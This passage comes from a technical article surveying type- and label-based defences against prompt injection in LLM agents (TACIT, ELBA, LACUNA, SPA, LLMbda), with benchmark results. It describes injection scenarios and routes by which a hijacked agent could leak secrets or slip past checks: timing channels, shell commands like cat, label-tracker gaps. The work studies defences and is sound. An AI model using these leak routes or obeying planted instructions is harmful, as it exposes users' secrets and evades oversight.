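The square brackets contain the permitted effects, and `AskFirst` requires a request for approval before the first email. The compiler's theory turns this rule into a finite automaton, a machine with a fixed number of states:

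| State | After a request for approval | After an email |
|---|---|---|
| nobody asked yet | asked | violation |
| asked | asked | asked |

From the function's code, the compiler also derives a summary $A$ of the sequences of effects it might produce. If $P$ is the set of sequences the rule permits, the function is safe when

$$\text{every beginning of every sequence in } A \text{ is in } P$$

This is decidable because finite automata can describe both sets. For the function above, $A$ contains "ask" and "ask, send", so the compiler can accept it. If every sequence in $A$ breaks the rule, the compiler rejects the function. If only some do, it adds a monitor that follows the automaton while the program runs.

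Summaries carry over from one function to the next, so a rule also covers work an agent delegates. Tan and colleagues cite a fault in Goose, a coding agent, in which a sub-agent ran tools without the approval its parent session required.

However, the rule only requires the program to request approval before it sends email. One request permits any number of later emails, even if the answer is no. In the example, the `if` checks the answer, and separate code in the software that runs the program has to check that the approval was for this particular report. ETAS also doesn't track where data came from. An email to Eve has the same effect as one to Bob and comes at the same point in the order, so the type check treats them alike.

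Tan and colleagues have built a compiler and an interpreter, and prove their main guarantees for a simplified core of the language. In small tests, the compiler accepted two correct programs and rejected four faulty ones. A coding agent written in ETAS behaved as expected in ten scenarios with scripted model replies. The team tested the automata, including the mixed case that needs a monitor, in a separate Python program. The paper compares the full design with other languages, but the prototype supports only part of that design. The paper includes no tests against prompt injection.

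### What these languages can't express

SPA's restrictions rule out some ordinary tasks. A plan can't repeat a search until it finds something, because loops only go through an existing collection. Variables created inside a loop disappear when the loop ends, so a plan can fetch every page on a list of unknown length but can't combine them into one summary afterwards.

An SPA plan can't do arithmetic. If the user asks the agent to pay half of the latest electricity bill, SPA needs a tool that divides numbers, or it has to ask the quarantined model. If the bill comes from a trusted source, the model's answer counts as trusted even if it is wrong. The simpler language can therefore move the division from code, which would get it right, to a model that might not. *Language-Based Agent Control* describes a similar limitation in agents that have a fixed set of tools and can't write programs. To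 find the earliest of several papers, such an agent has to read the entries one by one instead of sorting them.

Only SPA's tests indicate roughly how often models write unusable plans. With the label checks off and the tools visible, about 19% of single-request runs never reached execution, a figure that includes malformed plans. Only 53% completed the task, so many plans that did run were wrong or incomplete. A stronger model would probably do better on both measures.

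A better planner would help less with the labels. With the checks on, SPA rejected about 53% of the plans for breaking a label rule, mostly because they passed a tool's untrusted output to a tool that required trusted data. Many tasks require this, so even a perfect planner couldn't write an acceptable plan for them. Girrens and Wang suggest separate labels for each field, separate limits for each argument, and endorsement after an explicit check. FIDES and Prudentia already have versions of all three, but developers must get more labels right and users must answer more questions.

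## Capabilities tracked by a compiler: TACIT in Scala

SPA's language is easy to check because it leaves out most of the features programmers normally use. TACIT, which a group at EPFL in Lausanne published in March 2026, keeps almost all of them. Its agents write programs in Scala 3, a general-purpose language with recursion and user-defined functions, and a program can run only if the compiler accepts it.

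TACIT (Tracked Agent Capabilities in Types) relies on the Scala compiler to establish which permissions each piece of an agent's program can use. This is simpler than working out everything the program will do, which no compiler can do. In *Tracking Capabilities for Safer Agents*, Odersky, Zhao and colleagues (2026) assume that the cloud-hosted model writing the programs may be cooperating fully with an attacker. They trust the compiler, the software that runs the compiled programs, TACIT's library and, optionally, a second model that handles secrets.

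A request goes through these steps:

```
1  the cloud model writes a Scala program
2  the compiler checks the whole program
       rejected:  nothing runs, and the model receives the error message
       accepted:  the program runs
3  the program uses TACIT's library to reach files, commands and websites
4  its output goes back to the cloud model
```

A type error in the last line therefore stops the first line from running. Unlike SPA, TACIT lets the model correct a rejected program. The program hasn't opened any files at that point, so the error message can't contain new text from an attacker.

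TACIT connects to existing agents, such as Claude Code, through MCP, a common standard for giving agents tools. The project's GitHub page, lampepfl's *TACIT*, recommends switching off the agent's built-in tools, because otherwise the model could bypass the compiler by using the ordinary shell.

### Capture sets

In Scala, a capability is an ordinary value, such as an open file, that lets code do something. The compiler records in each value's type which capabilities that value can use. Suppose `f` is a file, and a program defines a function that writes text to it:

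```
(s: String) => f.write(s)        type:  String ->{f} Unit
```

`Unit` means that the function returns nothing useful. The braces contain its capture set, the list of capabilities it may use. A function with an empty capture set is pure, and its type has a plain arrow:

```
(s: String) => s.length          type:  String -> Int
```

The pure function can compute a length, but it can't write to a file, contact a website or print anything, because each of these needs a capability. A function with a smaller capture set can always stand in for one with a larger set. With $<:$ for "can stand in for", the rule is

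$$C_1 \subseteq C_2 \;\Rightarrow\; (A \to B)^{C_1} <: (A \to B)^{C_2}$$

The reverse doesn't hold, so a program can't use the file-writing function where the library requires a pure one.

The compiler still tracks the file when another object wraps it. Scala's *Tracked Capabilities Overview* gives the example of a logger that writes messages to a file. The logger's type includes the file in its capture set, so a function that uses the logger isn't pure.

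The compiler checks each function against the declared types of the functions it calls, so it doesn't have to trace data through the whole program. TACIT can therefore allow recursion and functions that take other functions as arguments, which CaMeL's interpreter and SPA leave out or restrict.

### A wrapper for secrets

When a program reads a file from a protected folder, TACIT's library returns the contents in a wrapper called `Classified`. In simplified form:

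```
trait Classified[T]:
  def map[U](op: T -> U): Classified[U]
```

`map` applies a function to the contents and puts the result in a new wrapper. The function must be pure because the parameter's type uses the plain arrow. Odersky and colleagues call this local purity. The code that handles the secret can't write files or use the network, though the rest of the program still may.

The compiler accepts this program, in which `chat` sends text to the trusted model:

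```
requestFileSystem("/project") {
  val doc     = readClassified("/project/secrets/contract.txt")
  val summary = chat(doc.map(d => "Summarise this contract: " + d))
  writeClassified("/project/secrets/summary.txt", summary)
}
```

The function inside `map` only joins two pieces of text. The contract, the prompt and the summary all stay in wrappers.

The compiler rejects the next program, which comes from the group's tests (shortened here):

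```
requestFileSystem("secrets") {
  val githubKey = readClassified("/secrets/api-keys/github.txt")
  githubKey.map { key => println(key) }
}

Found:     String ->{io} Unit
Required:  String -> Unit
```

Printing needs the `io` capability, so a function that prints isn't pure. A program might instead copy the key into a mutable variable inside `map` and print the variable afterwards. This also fails, because Scala treats mutable variables as capabilities.

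### Why a file permission can't outlive its block

`requestFileSystem` creates a permission for one folder, passes it to a block of code and returns the block's result. The permission is valid only while the block runs. An agent might try to keep it by returning a function that reads a file later:

```
val later = requestFileSystem("/project") { fs =>
  () => fs.access("notes.txt").read()
}
later()
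```

The returned function has the type `() ->{fs} String`. The variable `later` would need the same type, but `fs` exists only inside the block, so that type has no meaning outside it and the compiler rejects the program. If the block had returned the text of the notes, the compiler would have accepted the program, because text holds no permission.

PACE also limits how long a capability lasts, but it checks the expiry time when the agent makes a call. In TACIT, the compiler rejects a program that tries to keep a file permission for too long, so the program never starts.

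Types don't cover every limit. The compiler can verify that code holds a file permission, but the library has to check at run time that each path is inside the permitted folder. It also checks commands and website names at run time.

The program the agent writes also requests the folder, commands and websites it will use. In March 2026, the documented settings included no limit on which folders or websites it could request, so a hijacked model could write a program that requests more access. Later documentation, copied in Glama's *TACIT*, describes settings that limit all three. By default, agents can now use only the folder in which TACIT was started, but they can still request any website unless someone sets a limit.

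### Unsafe features that agents can't use

Scala has features that let programmers override the type system. An agent could use them to hide a capability, so TACIT restricts the agent's programs to a subset of the language called safe mode.

| Safe mode forbids | Without this rule, a program could |
|---|---|
| Unchecked type casts and pattern matches | relabel a file-writing function as pure |
| The `caps.unsafe` module | use a capability without the compiler tracking it |
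| `@unchecked` annotations | switch off a check for one piece of code |
| Runtime reflection | look up a method by name and call it without the compiler seeing which one it is |
| Compiling without capture checking, including for changeable variables | copy a secret from `map` into an outside variable |
| Global library code that isn't known to be safe | write files through an ordinary library that needs no capability |

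Some library code needs these features internally. Its author can mark it `@assumeSafe`, which makes it available to agents. Scala's *Safe Mode* gives the example of a mail function that asks the user before sending each message. The agent can call this function but not the underlying mailer. The compiler doesn't verify the mark, so a mistake in the marked code could let an agent bypass the restrictions.

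Safe mode allows exceptions, the errors that interrupt a running program, even though a program could put a secret in an error message. Tracking every possible exception in the types would be impractical, because even dividing by zero or running out of memory raises one. TACIT instead catches exceptions at run time and hides any that involve classified data. A failed operation on a secret can therefore look to the agent like a success with no output, and in one test the researchers had to warn the agents about this.

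TACIT's enforcement was at first weaker than its design suggests. In March 2026, a separate program searched the agent's code for forbidden patterns, the same kind of text matching that works badly for shell commands. In *Scala 3.8.3 is now available!*, Mazur announced an experimental safe mode in the compiler itself. Later versions of TACIT use safe mode by default, together with the pattern search.

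### Separate outputs for the user and the cloud model

The user may need to see a secret that the cloud model must not see. TACIT therefore has two output channels. Ordinary text goes to both, but a classified value appears differently on each:

```
println(summary)

the user's terminal:   The supplier may now end the contract with 30 days' notice.
the cloud model:       Classified(****)
```

The wrapper stays in place in later turns. If the user asks how long the summary is, the agent can write `summary.map(_.length)` and print the result. The user sees the number, but the cloud model again receives only asterisks.

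The cloud model can't summarise a contract it can't read, so it passes the contract to the trusted model, which has no tools. Unlike the quarantined model in Willison's design, the trusted model is also used to keep secrets from the cloud provider, so whoever operates it has to be trustworthy.

A call to `chat` needs no capability, so it counts as pure and a program may use it inside `map`. This is justified only if the model's host keeps the text private and doesn't reuse it when answering later requests, which the compiler can't check. TACIT accepts the address of any compatible service, so the "local" model is local only if whoever installs TACIT chooses a local service.

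### The leak tests

To test for leaks, the team built a small software project with a folder of API keys, a database and confidential documents. Some of the 12 legitimate tasks used only ordinary files, while others, such as summarising a confidential incident report, needed the secrets. The team combined each task with 10 injections, for 120 trials. Some injections were disguised as system messages or included claims that the secrets were only test data, and others contained ready-made Scala code for reading the secret files.

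Another 11 trials involved an openly malicious user instead of an injection. In five, the user asked directly for secrets, and in six, the user posed as an authority, such as an administrator changing passwords in an emergency.

Each model ran all 131 trials with the wrapper and again with the secrets as plain text. The table shows the share of trials in which no secret appeared in the agent's output.

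| Model | Trials | Protection on | Protection off |
|---|---|---|---|
| Claude Sonnet 4.6 | 120 with injections | 100% | 100% |
| Claude Sonnet 4.6 | 11 malicious requests | 100% | 81.8% |
| Claude Sonnet 4.6 | All 131 | 100% | 98.5% |
| MiniMax M2.5 | 120 with injections | 100% | 97.5% |
| MiniMax M2.5 | 11 malicious requests | 100% | 27.3% |
| MiniMax M2.5 | All 131 | 100% | 91.6% |

With the protection off, MiniMax leaked secrets in 8 of the 11 malicious trials. The overall figure was still 91.6% because most trials used injections, which both models usually resisted.

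The design should produce perfect scores with the protection on, so these results mainly confirm that the implementation had no obvious hole. The experiment used a fixed set of attacks and didn't include a systematic search for programs that the compiler wrongly accepts.

The agents could still do legitimate work with the protection on. Sonnet completed 99.2% of the legitimate tasks and MiniMax 90.0%, compared with 83.3% and 88.3% with the protection off. Sonnet's lower score without protection may be an artefact of the test, because it often ran out of time or turns and sometimes stopped to warn the user about an injection.

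### TACIT on AgentDojo

The researchers also adapted AgentDojo's four suites to TACIT. Tools that return text from other people, such as emails, web pages and hotel reviews, now wrap it in `Classified`. The cloud model never reads this text, and a quarantined model extracts or summarises what the user needs.

AgentDojo counted one of 1,926 attacks on two models as a success. The user had asked the agent to book a particular hotel, and the attacker had planted a recommendation for another hotel in the reviews. The agent booked the right hotel but quoted the reviews to the user, and AgentDojo's scorer found the other hotel's name in the text. The policy allowed the agent to show public reviews, so the compiler had not missed a violation.

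The next table compares the share of tasks completed with CaMeL's published results on the same models.

| Suite | Gemini 2.5 Pro: CaMeL | Gemini 2.5 Pro: TACIT | o4-mini: CaMeL | o4-mini: TACIT |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| Banking | 52.8% | 56.9% | 62.5% | 59.0% |
| Workspace | 53.8% | 50.5% | 81.4% | 52.9% |
| Slack | 48.6% | 40.0% | 68.6% | 47.6% |
| Travel | 1.4% | 64.3% | 74.3% | 68.6% |

Odersky and colleagues' description of the two systems as comparable is fair for banking, but with o4-mini, CaMeL completed far more of the workspace and Slack tasks. CaMeL's extremely low result on travel with Gemini looks like a failure specific to that combination, since CaMeL did well on travel with o4-mini.

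It is unclear how well this test checks local purity. No capability appears in the published descriptions of tools such as `sendMoney`, and the agents are told that any side effect inside `map` happens immediately. If the compiler allows a payment inside `map`, an attacker who changes the account number on a bill could redirect the money. If it doesn't, the agent can't pay a bill whose account number appears only in a classified file.

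### The cost of writing typed programs

Ordinary agents write tool calls in JSON, which models have seen far more often than Scala with capture sets. To test whether switching to Scala makes agents perform worse, the team used *τ²-Bench* (Barres, Dong and colleagues, 2025), a benchmark of customer service conversations. A second language model plays the customer, who might want to change a flight or return an order. The agent must find out what the customer wants, follow the company's written policy and make the right changes in a database. Code then checks the final state of the database and whether the agent gave the customer the required information.

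The TACIT team used the 50 airline tasks and 115 retail tasks, with ten runs of each:

| Model | Airline: tool calls | Airline: TACIT | Retail: tool calls | Retail: TACIT |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| gpt-oss-120b | 43.8% | 45.2% | 53.3% | 57.0% |
| MiniMax M2.5 | 58.4% | 61.0% | 75.1% | 77.5% |
| DeepSeek V3.2 | 57.8% | 58.6% | 74.6% | 75.5% |

TACIT gained between 0.8 and 3.7 percentage points. Most of these differences are small enough to be due to chance, but all six favour TACIT, so writing Scala did no visible harm. Odersky and colleagues suggest that the models benefited from clearly structured results and the compiler's error messages.

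The models rarely had to resubmit their code. Depending on the model and the suite, 0.32% to 7.93% of programs needed at least one retry, and those needed 1.06 to 1.39 retries on average. Common mistakes included failing to handle missing values and mistyping dollar amounts, because the dollar sign can have a special meaning in Scala strings. The compiler checks a typical program in under a second, and capture checking is only part of that work. *What's in the Box* (2025), an earlier paper on the same type system, measured capture checking at less than 15% of compilation time for Scala's standard library on an ordinary desktop computer.

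On SWE-bench Lite, where agents fix real bugs from GitHub, MiniMax M2.5 resolved 41.7% of 300 issues with TACIT and 43.3% with ordinary tools. The five-issue difference could easily be chance. The researchers suspect that such work depends more on shell commands, which are awkward to express through TACIT's library.

The customer service results are a better measure of how much typed Scala hinders an agent than of how much capability restrictions do. The published tools, such as `cancelReservation(reservationId: String)`, take no capability as an argument, so the agents seldom had to deal with one.

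LACUNA, a later system from the same group, had more trouble. Its Scala programs contain gaps that a model fills with code while the program runs. The compiler checks each piece of code before it runs, so rejected code does no damage, but an agent that can't write acceptable code makes no progress. *LACUNA* (Zhao, Xu and colleagues, 2026) tested the system on all 392 τ²-bench tasks. DeepSeek V4 Flash solved 76.0% of them with LACUNA, compared with 90.0% with ordinary tool calls. The compiler rejected 22.4% of this model's code on the retail tasks. It rejected only 3.2% of the weaker Gemini 3.1 Flash-Lite's code on those tasks, but 89% on the phone support tasks.

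In TACIT, the cloud model has to write the function for `map` without seeing the secret document, so the function can't adapt to its contents. LACUNA solves this by letting a trusted local model write code inside `map` after reading the document. The compiler also checks this code and rejects it if it isn't pure.

On AgentDojo, 8 of 1,898 attacks succeeded against LACUNA, 7 of them with Gemini 2.5 Pro. Zhao and colleagues point out that an attacker can still persuade a model to misuse a permission the task requires.

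### What the compiler can't guarantee

The `Classified` wrapper records that data is secret but not whether an attacker may have changed it. In Bob's request, suppose the meeting notes are classified and the email tool takes an ordinary string as the recipient. The trusted model can extract Bob's address, but the result is still wrapped, so the compiler rejects the call to the email tool. A developer could add an email tool that accepts wrapped addresses, but that tool would also accept Eve's address.

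The later documentation on Glama states that the wrapper protects "confidentiality, not integrity". An agent can wrap any text and write it over a protected file, such as the list of keys that grant login access to the computer. Administrators can forbid such writes, but TACIT allows them by default.

The later version also lets agents send classified data to permitted websites, for instance to log in with a secret key. The website receives the key without the agent ever seeing it. If the permitted sites include one where anyone can publish, a hijacked agent might be able to post a secret there.

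The types don't show whether an answer is right. An agent's program can pass every check and still summarise the wrong contract or cancel the wrong booking.

Secrets can also leak through timing. A pure function can take a long time if a key starts with A and finish immediately otherwise. The cloud model receives only asterisks, but the delay may reveal whether the key starts with A. Repeating this with other tests could slowly reveal more. Odersky and colleagues exclude timing leaks from their guarantee.

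The guarantee also depends on the type system and the compiler being correct. Earlier work included computer-checked proofs about the basic type system, but Odersky and colleagues note that safe mode still lacks a full proof. *System Capybara* (Xu, Bračevac and colleagues, 2026) later proved in Lean that programs in a small core language read, write and use up only what their capture sets allow. The proof doesn't cover the full compiler, safe mode or TACIT's library of about 1,000 lines. Capture checking is also still experimental. *Classifying Capabilities (Extended Version)* (Pham, Bračevac and colleagues, 2026) reports that parts of the standard library had remained outside capture checking because the types couldn't express the necessary restrictions, and proposes an extension that can.

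External programs are the largest practical gap in TACIT's protection. If an agent may run `cat`, it can print a secret file and receive the contents as ordinary text, because the compiler checks only the request to run a command. TACIT can block `cat` and similar commands, but other tools also read files. Odersky and colleagues suggest allowing only specific commands, such as `git diff` and `sbt`. But even `git diff` prints recent changes to any secret file that the project tracks, and `sbt`, Scala's build tool, like `npm test`, runs code from a project file that the agent may be able to edit. For sensitive work, the researchers therefore recommend running TACIT inside a sandbox.

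## Policies written as types for the whole application: ELBA in Haskell

TACIT checks the programs that an agent writes, but not the software around the agent, which starts it, uses its answers and may call other agents. That software can also leak data. Tan and colleagues point out that in frameworks such as LangGraph, developers connect agents through callbacks and task graphs whose ordinary types don't describe what the agents may do.

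*Language-Based Agent Control* (Zhou, D'Antoni and Polikarpova, 2026) proposes writing the application and the agent's programs in the same typed language, so that one type checker covers both. The paper's implementation, ELBA, uses Haskell, where a piece of code's type shows what effects it can have.

### An agent call with an expected type

In ELBA, developers call an agent like any other function:

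```
agent :: Defs -> Prompt -> t
```

`Defs` is the set of functions and types the agent may use, and `t` is the type of result the surrounding code expects. When the application reaches this call, ELBA asks the model for a Haskell program of type `t`, checks its type and runs it. If the check fails, the model receives the error message and tries again.

The expected type limits what the agent can do because ordinary Haskell code that reads a file or contacts a website has a type marked `IO`, and one such step marks the whole program. In the simplest example, a public calculator calls an agent that must return an `Int`, a whole number. If a visitor asks it to delete the server's files and then compute a factorial, the model might write a program that does both. That program has the type `IO Int`, so ELBA rejects it.

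A few Haskell functions can hide an effect from the type checker. Safe Haskell, a restricted form of the language, excludes them, much as Scala's safe mode does for TACIT.

### A bibliography without invented entries

An agent that can only compute isn't much use. The paper's main example is an agent that searches for papers and writes a bibliography, under the rule that every entry must come from DBLP, a database of computer science publications. The developer defines a new kind of effect, `BibIO`, and three functions that use it. In simplified form:

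```
dblpSearch      :: String      -> BibIO [DOI]
dblpFetchBib    :: DOI         -> BibIO (Trusted Bib)
appendToBibFile :: Trusted Bib -> BibIO ()
```

A DOI is a paper's permanent identifier. `Trusted Bib` is a bibliography entry in a wrapper that only the developer's library can create. The agent's program must have the type `BibIO ()`, which means it may use these effects and returns nothing.

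Suppose the user wants the earliest paper on a subject. The agent can write a program that fetches all the matching entries, sorts them by year and appends the first. Sorting has no effects, so the agent can do it however it likes. If the model instead tries to add a paper it has made up, it has three obvious routes:

| The agent's program | Why the type checker rejects it |
|---|---|
| passes its own text to `appendToBibFile` | the function needs a `Trusted Bib`, and the text is a `String` |
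| puts its own text in a `Trusted` wrapper | the library doesn't export the function that creates the wrapper |
| writes the file with Haskell's standard `writeFile` | the result is `IO ()`, and the call expects `BibIO ()` |

Zhou and colleagues tested this agent on 100 computer science topics with Claude Sonnet 5. None of its 925 citations had a wrong author, year or DOI, compared with 19 of 1,002 from an ordinary agent with a web search tool. The ordinary agent also used 65 times as many input tokens. The two agents had different sources as well as different rules, so some of the improvement may come from having access to DBLP. The types also can't check whether an entry is relevant, so the agent could still fill the bibliography with real papers on the wrong subject.

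### Sub-agents inherit their parent's limits

ELBA requires a complete program each time, but that program can call an agent to look at a result and choose the next step. For example, the bibliography agent might fetch one search result, put it in a sub-agent's prompt and let the sub-agent decide whether to refine the search.

The parent's program has the type `BibIO ()`, so Haskell infers that a sub-agent finishing the job must have that type too. The sub-agent therefore can't call `writeFile`, even if the search result contains a planted instruction to do so. The parent can't lift this restriction by asking for an `IO ()` sub-agent, because its own program would then fail the type check.

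The parent can impose a tighter policy. A parent that only needs to check whether an abstract is relevant can ask for a `Bool`, and the sub-agent then can't perform any effects. File permissions work similarly. In another of the team's examples, a program can open a file only through a value of type `Path`, which gives access to one folder and everything inside it. A parent with access to a project can give a sub-agent a `Path` for only the `drafts` folder.

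The paper proves that these limits hold however deeply the agents are nested. Let $\text{traces}(e)$ be all the sequences of tool calls that a program $e$ could make. A rule $P$ is a property of the type $t$ if

$$\text{for every program } e \text{ of type } t,\quad P(\text{traces}(e))$$

The theorem states that any such rule in the original language still holds after adding `agent` calls. The proof replaces each agent call with an ordinary function that asks the model for a program, checks its type and runs it. The result is an ordinary program of the same type, so the rule already applies to it. The new program may contain agent calls of its own, so the proof uses induction on the nesting depth, which ELBA limits.

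The proof holds whatever the model writes, but it assumes that Haskell's type system and the developer's library enforce the rule. It covers only tool calls, not what the company hosting the model learns from the prompts.

### Letting a sub-agent read untrusted data

`BibIO` determines which functions an agent can use, but some rules depend on what the agent has read. For these, ELBA uses LIO, a Haskell library for information-flow control that was more than a decade old when the team adopted it. Stefan, Russo and colleagues (2012), in *Flexible Dynamic Information Flow Control in the Presence of Exceptions*, describe its design. Each LIO program has a current label $L$, which works like the context label in FIDES, and a clearance $C$, which limits how far $L$ can rise. To read data with the label $\ell$, the program must satisfy the condition on the left, and $L$ then changes as shown on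 the right:

$$L \sqcup \ell \sqsubseteq C \qquad\qquad L := L \sqcup \ell$$

To write to a destination with the label $\ell$, it must satisfy $L \sqsubseteq \ell$.

The clearance prevents a program from reading certain data at all. A company could start one sub-agent per customer and give each a clearance that excludes the other customers' records.

The current label is necessary because ordinary variables have no labels. In an example from Hackage's *lio-0.11.6.0*, the library's documentation in Haskell's package archive, a program reads a secret into a variable. From then on, the current label has to protect everything the program can read.

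A program can avoid raising its own label by running part of its code separately with LIO's `toLabeled` function. The label can rise up to a set limit while that part runs. When it finishes, LIO restores the program's old label and returns the result in a closed wrapper that has its own label.

Running a sub-agent inside `toLabeled` gives much the same protection as Willison's quarantined model, but the sub-agent can keep its tools. Zhou and colleagues describe an agent that has to send someone a summary of an external email, using a link from untrusted text. A sub-agent follows the link, reads the email and returns a wrapped draft. It can use any tool that its lowered integrity permits, which excludes the one that sends messages. The main agent, whose label hasn't changed, passes the draft to that tool without opening it. In CaMeL, the quarantined model couldn't follow the link itself.

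The messaging tool takes the recipient as a plain value and the text in a wrapper, and it refuses to run if the caller's label is untrusted. An email tool built the same way would treat Bob's request like this:

```
address from the notes:
    the agent must open the wrapper  -> its label becomes untrusted -> refused

address typed by the user, document in a wrapper:
    the agent's label stays trusted  -> sent
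```

As in SPA, the first email fails whether the address is Bob's or Eve's. The messaging tool is designed to release whatever is in the wrapper, so an email tool would also need to check whether Bob may read the attachment.

LIO is backed by years of published proofs. For example, *Dynamic IFC Theorems for Free!* (2020) proves noninterference for a version of the library's core in Agda, a language for computer-checked proofs. But code inside `toLabeled` can leak a secret by never finishing, much like the timing leaks in TACIT. For this reason, a 2012 release of *lio* disables the function by default, and its Hackage page includes a warning about it. Stefan and colleagues exclude this leak from their guarantee and suggest using the clearance to keep untrusted code away from such secrets.

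### Which checks happen before the program runs

ELBA combines checks on the program's text with checks on the values that appear while it runs.

| Rule | When ELBA or its libraries check it |
|---|---|
| The program uses only the permitted kind of effect | before it runs |
| Bibliography entries come from DBLP | before it runs |
| The program opens files through a `Path`, not a text string | before it runs |
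| A path stays inside its folder, even through a symbolic link | while it runs |
| The current label permits a message or a web request | while it runs |

A program that fails one of the first three checks does nothing, so the model can safely try again. Such retries were rare in the AgentDojo experiments, averaging 0.13 per run, and 7 of 2,688 runs reached the retry limit.

A failed label check is harder to handle, because the program may already have sent two messages when LIO blocks the third. ELBA's retries don't cover such errors. The checks before execution apply to only one program at a time. A parent agent may change something before its sub-agent writes a program, so ELBA can't approve a whole task in advance as SPA does. *L3M* (2026), a later system that also limits model-written programs by their type, grades each effect by how reversible it is, which at least identifies the steps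 that software can't undo.

### Comparison with CaMeL on Slack tasks

The team compared ELBA with CaMeL on AgentDojo's Slack suite. They worded each attack in three ways, for a total of 315 attacked runs for each model and setting.

| Model | Policies | ELBA, no attack (of 21) | CaMeL, no attack (of 21) | ELBA, attacked | CaMeL, attacked |
|---|---|---|---|---|---|
| Claude Opus 4.7 | off | 18 | 15 | 83.8% | 67.0% |
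| Claude Opus 4.8 | off | 16 | 16 | 87.3% | 76.8% |
| GPT-5.4 | off | 16 | 17 | 77.1% | 78.7% |
| Claude Sonnet 5 | off | 14 | 13 | 74.6% | 53.7% |
| Claude Opus 4.7 | on | 10 | 5 | 48.6% | 21.9% |
| Claude Opus 4.8 | on | 9 | 6 | 44.8% | 28.3% |
| GPT-5.4 | on | 10 | 5 | 47.0% | 23.5% |
| Claude Sonnet 5 | on | 8 | 4 | 41.0% | 22.5% |

With policies on, ELBA completed almost twice as many tasks as CaMeL. With them off, its lead was much smaller, and CaMeL did slightly better with GPT-5.4. ELBA took about three times as long, mainly because its agents call the model again after reading data.

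That flexibility probably explains part of the lead, but the two systems also enforced different policies. ELBA's follow the principle that an agent that reads untrusted data should keep only the rights of whoever supplied it, so an agent that has read a message from Alice can still do what Alice could do. This is less restrictive than treating every outside source as equally untrusted, and CaMeL might have completed more tasks under a similar policy. The results with policies off don't isolate the effect of the design either, because CaMeL still plans before reading in that setting, while ELBA's Slack tools run with no restrictions.

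No attack succeeded against either system with any model, even with policies off, so the comparison provides no evidence about which is more secure.

### Sub-agents that obey every planted instruction

For a harder test, Zhou and colleagues assumed that the attacker had already compromised the model. ELBA's agents read all outside data through sub-agents, whose prompts contain the data and a task from the parent agent. The team changed the code to remove the task whenever the data contained AgentDojo's planted instruction, so the attacker's text was the only instruction the sub-agent received.

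They ran all 105 pairs seven times, which makes 735 attacked runs per model and setting:

| Model | Attacks resisted, policies off | Tasks completed, policies off | Attacks resisted, policies on | Tasks completed, policies on |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| Claude Opus 4.7 | 425 | 523 | 735 | 351 |
| Claude Opus 4.8 | 460 | 557 | 735 | 312 |
| GPT-5.4 | 621 | 558 | 735 | 338 |
| Claude Sonnet 5 | 540 | 494 | 735 | 294 |

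The GPT-5.4 counts follow from the percentages the paper gives with its margins of error. The paper also prints a conflicting set of counts, in which GPT-5.4 completes fewer tasks without policies (256) than with them (290). That is hard to reconcile with the model's other results.

Up to 42% of the attacks succeeded without policies, and none succeeded with them. AgentDojo's scorer counted just under 30 successes among the 2,940 runs with policies, but in each of those the agent had only opened a fixed web address, which the policies allow. The policies would have blocked the request if the address had contained private data or if the agent had already read something sensitive.

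This is better evidence for the policies than a zero on the ordinary benchmark, because the models weren't resisting the attacks. But it covers only five attacker goals, and a goal that the policies permit would have succeeded.

The policies reduced the share of completed tasks by 23 to 33 percentage points. Some of the lost completions had little value because the attack had also succeeded. Without policies, Opus 4.7 completed 523 tasks but resisted only 425 attacks, so in at least 98 runs it completed the user's task and also carried out the attack.

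However, most of the lost tasks are ones the policies block even when there is no attack. With policies on, the agents completed 38% to 48% of tasks without an attack and 40% to 48% in the worst case, so a compromised sub-agent barely affected task completion. Slack is also a hard case because the right calls often depend on the data.

Nobody could approve blocked calls in these tests. Like Prudentia's designers, Zhou and colleagues suggest using the policies to reduce the number of calls that need approval.

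### LACUNA: typed gaps in a Scala program

LACUNA, also from May 2026, applies much the same idea to the gaps in its Scala programs. Developers mark a gap with the call `agent[T](task)`, where `T` is the type that the model's code must have. A developer might write:

```
def isUrgent(report: String, log: ReadOnlyFile): Boolean =
  agent("Is this report urgent? Check the log if you need to.")
```

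With Scala's capture checking on, the model's code can read the log because permission to read it is in scope at the gap. The code can't send the log anywhere without a network capability, and it must return true or false.

To check the code, LACUNA inserts it into a copy of the surrounding source text and runs the Scala compiler again with the same settings. If the compiler rejects it, the model receives the errors and can try again. In LACUNA's evaluation of this step, the compiler correctly handled all of the roughly 400 combinations of program and inserted code, some valid and some faulty.

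In ELBA, developers grant permissions by listing the functions the agent may use and setting the type of effect. In LACUNA, the agent gets everything in scope at the gap, which is convenient but makes it easy to grant too much by accident. Developers can avoid this by putting the call in a small separate function, as above, so that the agent can't reach the caller's local variables and capabilities.

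Filling typed gaps was harder for the models than making ordinary tool calls. On the customer service tasks of τ²-bench, models completed fewer tasks overall with LACUNA than with tool calls. The largest drop for DeepSeek V4 Flash was on retail tasks, where it solved 58.8% with LACUNA and 80.9% with tool calls, and needed an average of 7.1 rewrites per task. The difference was smaller on airline tasks, where it solved 70.0% with LACUNA and 75.5% with tool calls.

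The compiler rejected less code on BrowseComp-Plus, a set of 830 difficult research questions about a fixed collection of documents. It rejected 8.6% of DeepSeek's programs, and the agent answered 27.1% of the questions correctly. The evaluation didn't include an ordinary agent with the same model and search tools, so the result doesn't show whether the types made the agent less accurate.

In seven of eight combinations of AgentDojo suite and model, LACUNA's task completion rate was 2 to 7 percentage points higher than the rate Odersky and colleagues had reported for TACIT. The low number of successful attacks against LACUNA probably understates the risk, because the models could still recognise and ignore a planted instruction. The ELBA team forced its models to obey such instructions, but LACUNA's designers did not. A model that obeyed could have used every permission in scope at the gap.

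## A machine-checked proof for the agent's interpreter: LLMbda

Labels protect data only if the software that tracks them never loses one. In work that first appeared in February 2026, Garby, Gordon and Sands found that CaMeL's tracker sometimes loses labels. For instance, when a CaMeL program inserts untrusted text into a longer string, the result counts as trusted. An attacker's email address could therefore pass a policy that requires a trusted recipient if the program had first put it through a text template. Such faults are hard to find because CaMeL has no formal definition of how labels should spread, and its Python code is the only reference.

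Garby and colleagues responded with LLMbda, a small language for writing agents, and a machine-checked proof that its label rules track every dependency of the kinds the proof covers.

### How an untaken branch reveals a secret

Some of the hardest dependencies to track come from code that doesn't run. Suppose a tracker marks a variable as secret whenever the program changes it inside a branch that depends on a secret. That sounds thorough, but this program defeats it:

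```
1  a = false
2  b = false
3  if secret then a = true
4  if not a  then b = true
5  publish b
```

| | If the secret is true | If the secret is false |
|---|---|---|
| After line 3 | `a` is true, labelled secret | `a` is false, labelled public |
| After line 4 | `b` is false, labelled public | `b` is true, labelled public |
| Line 5 | publishes false | publishes true |

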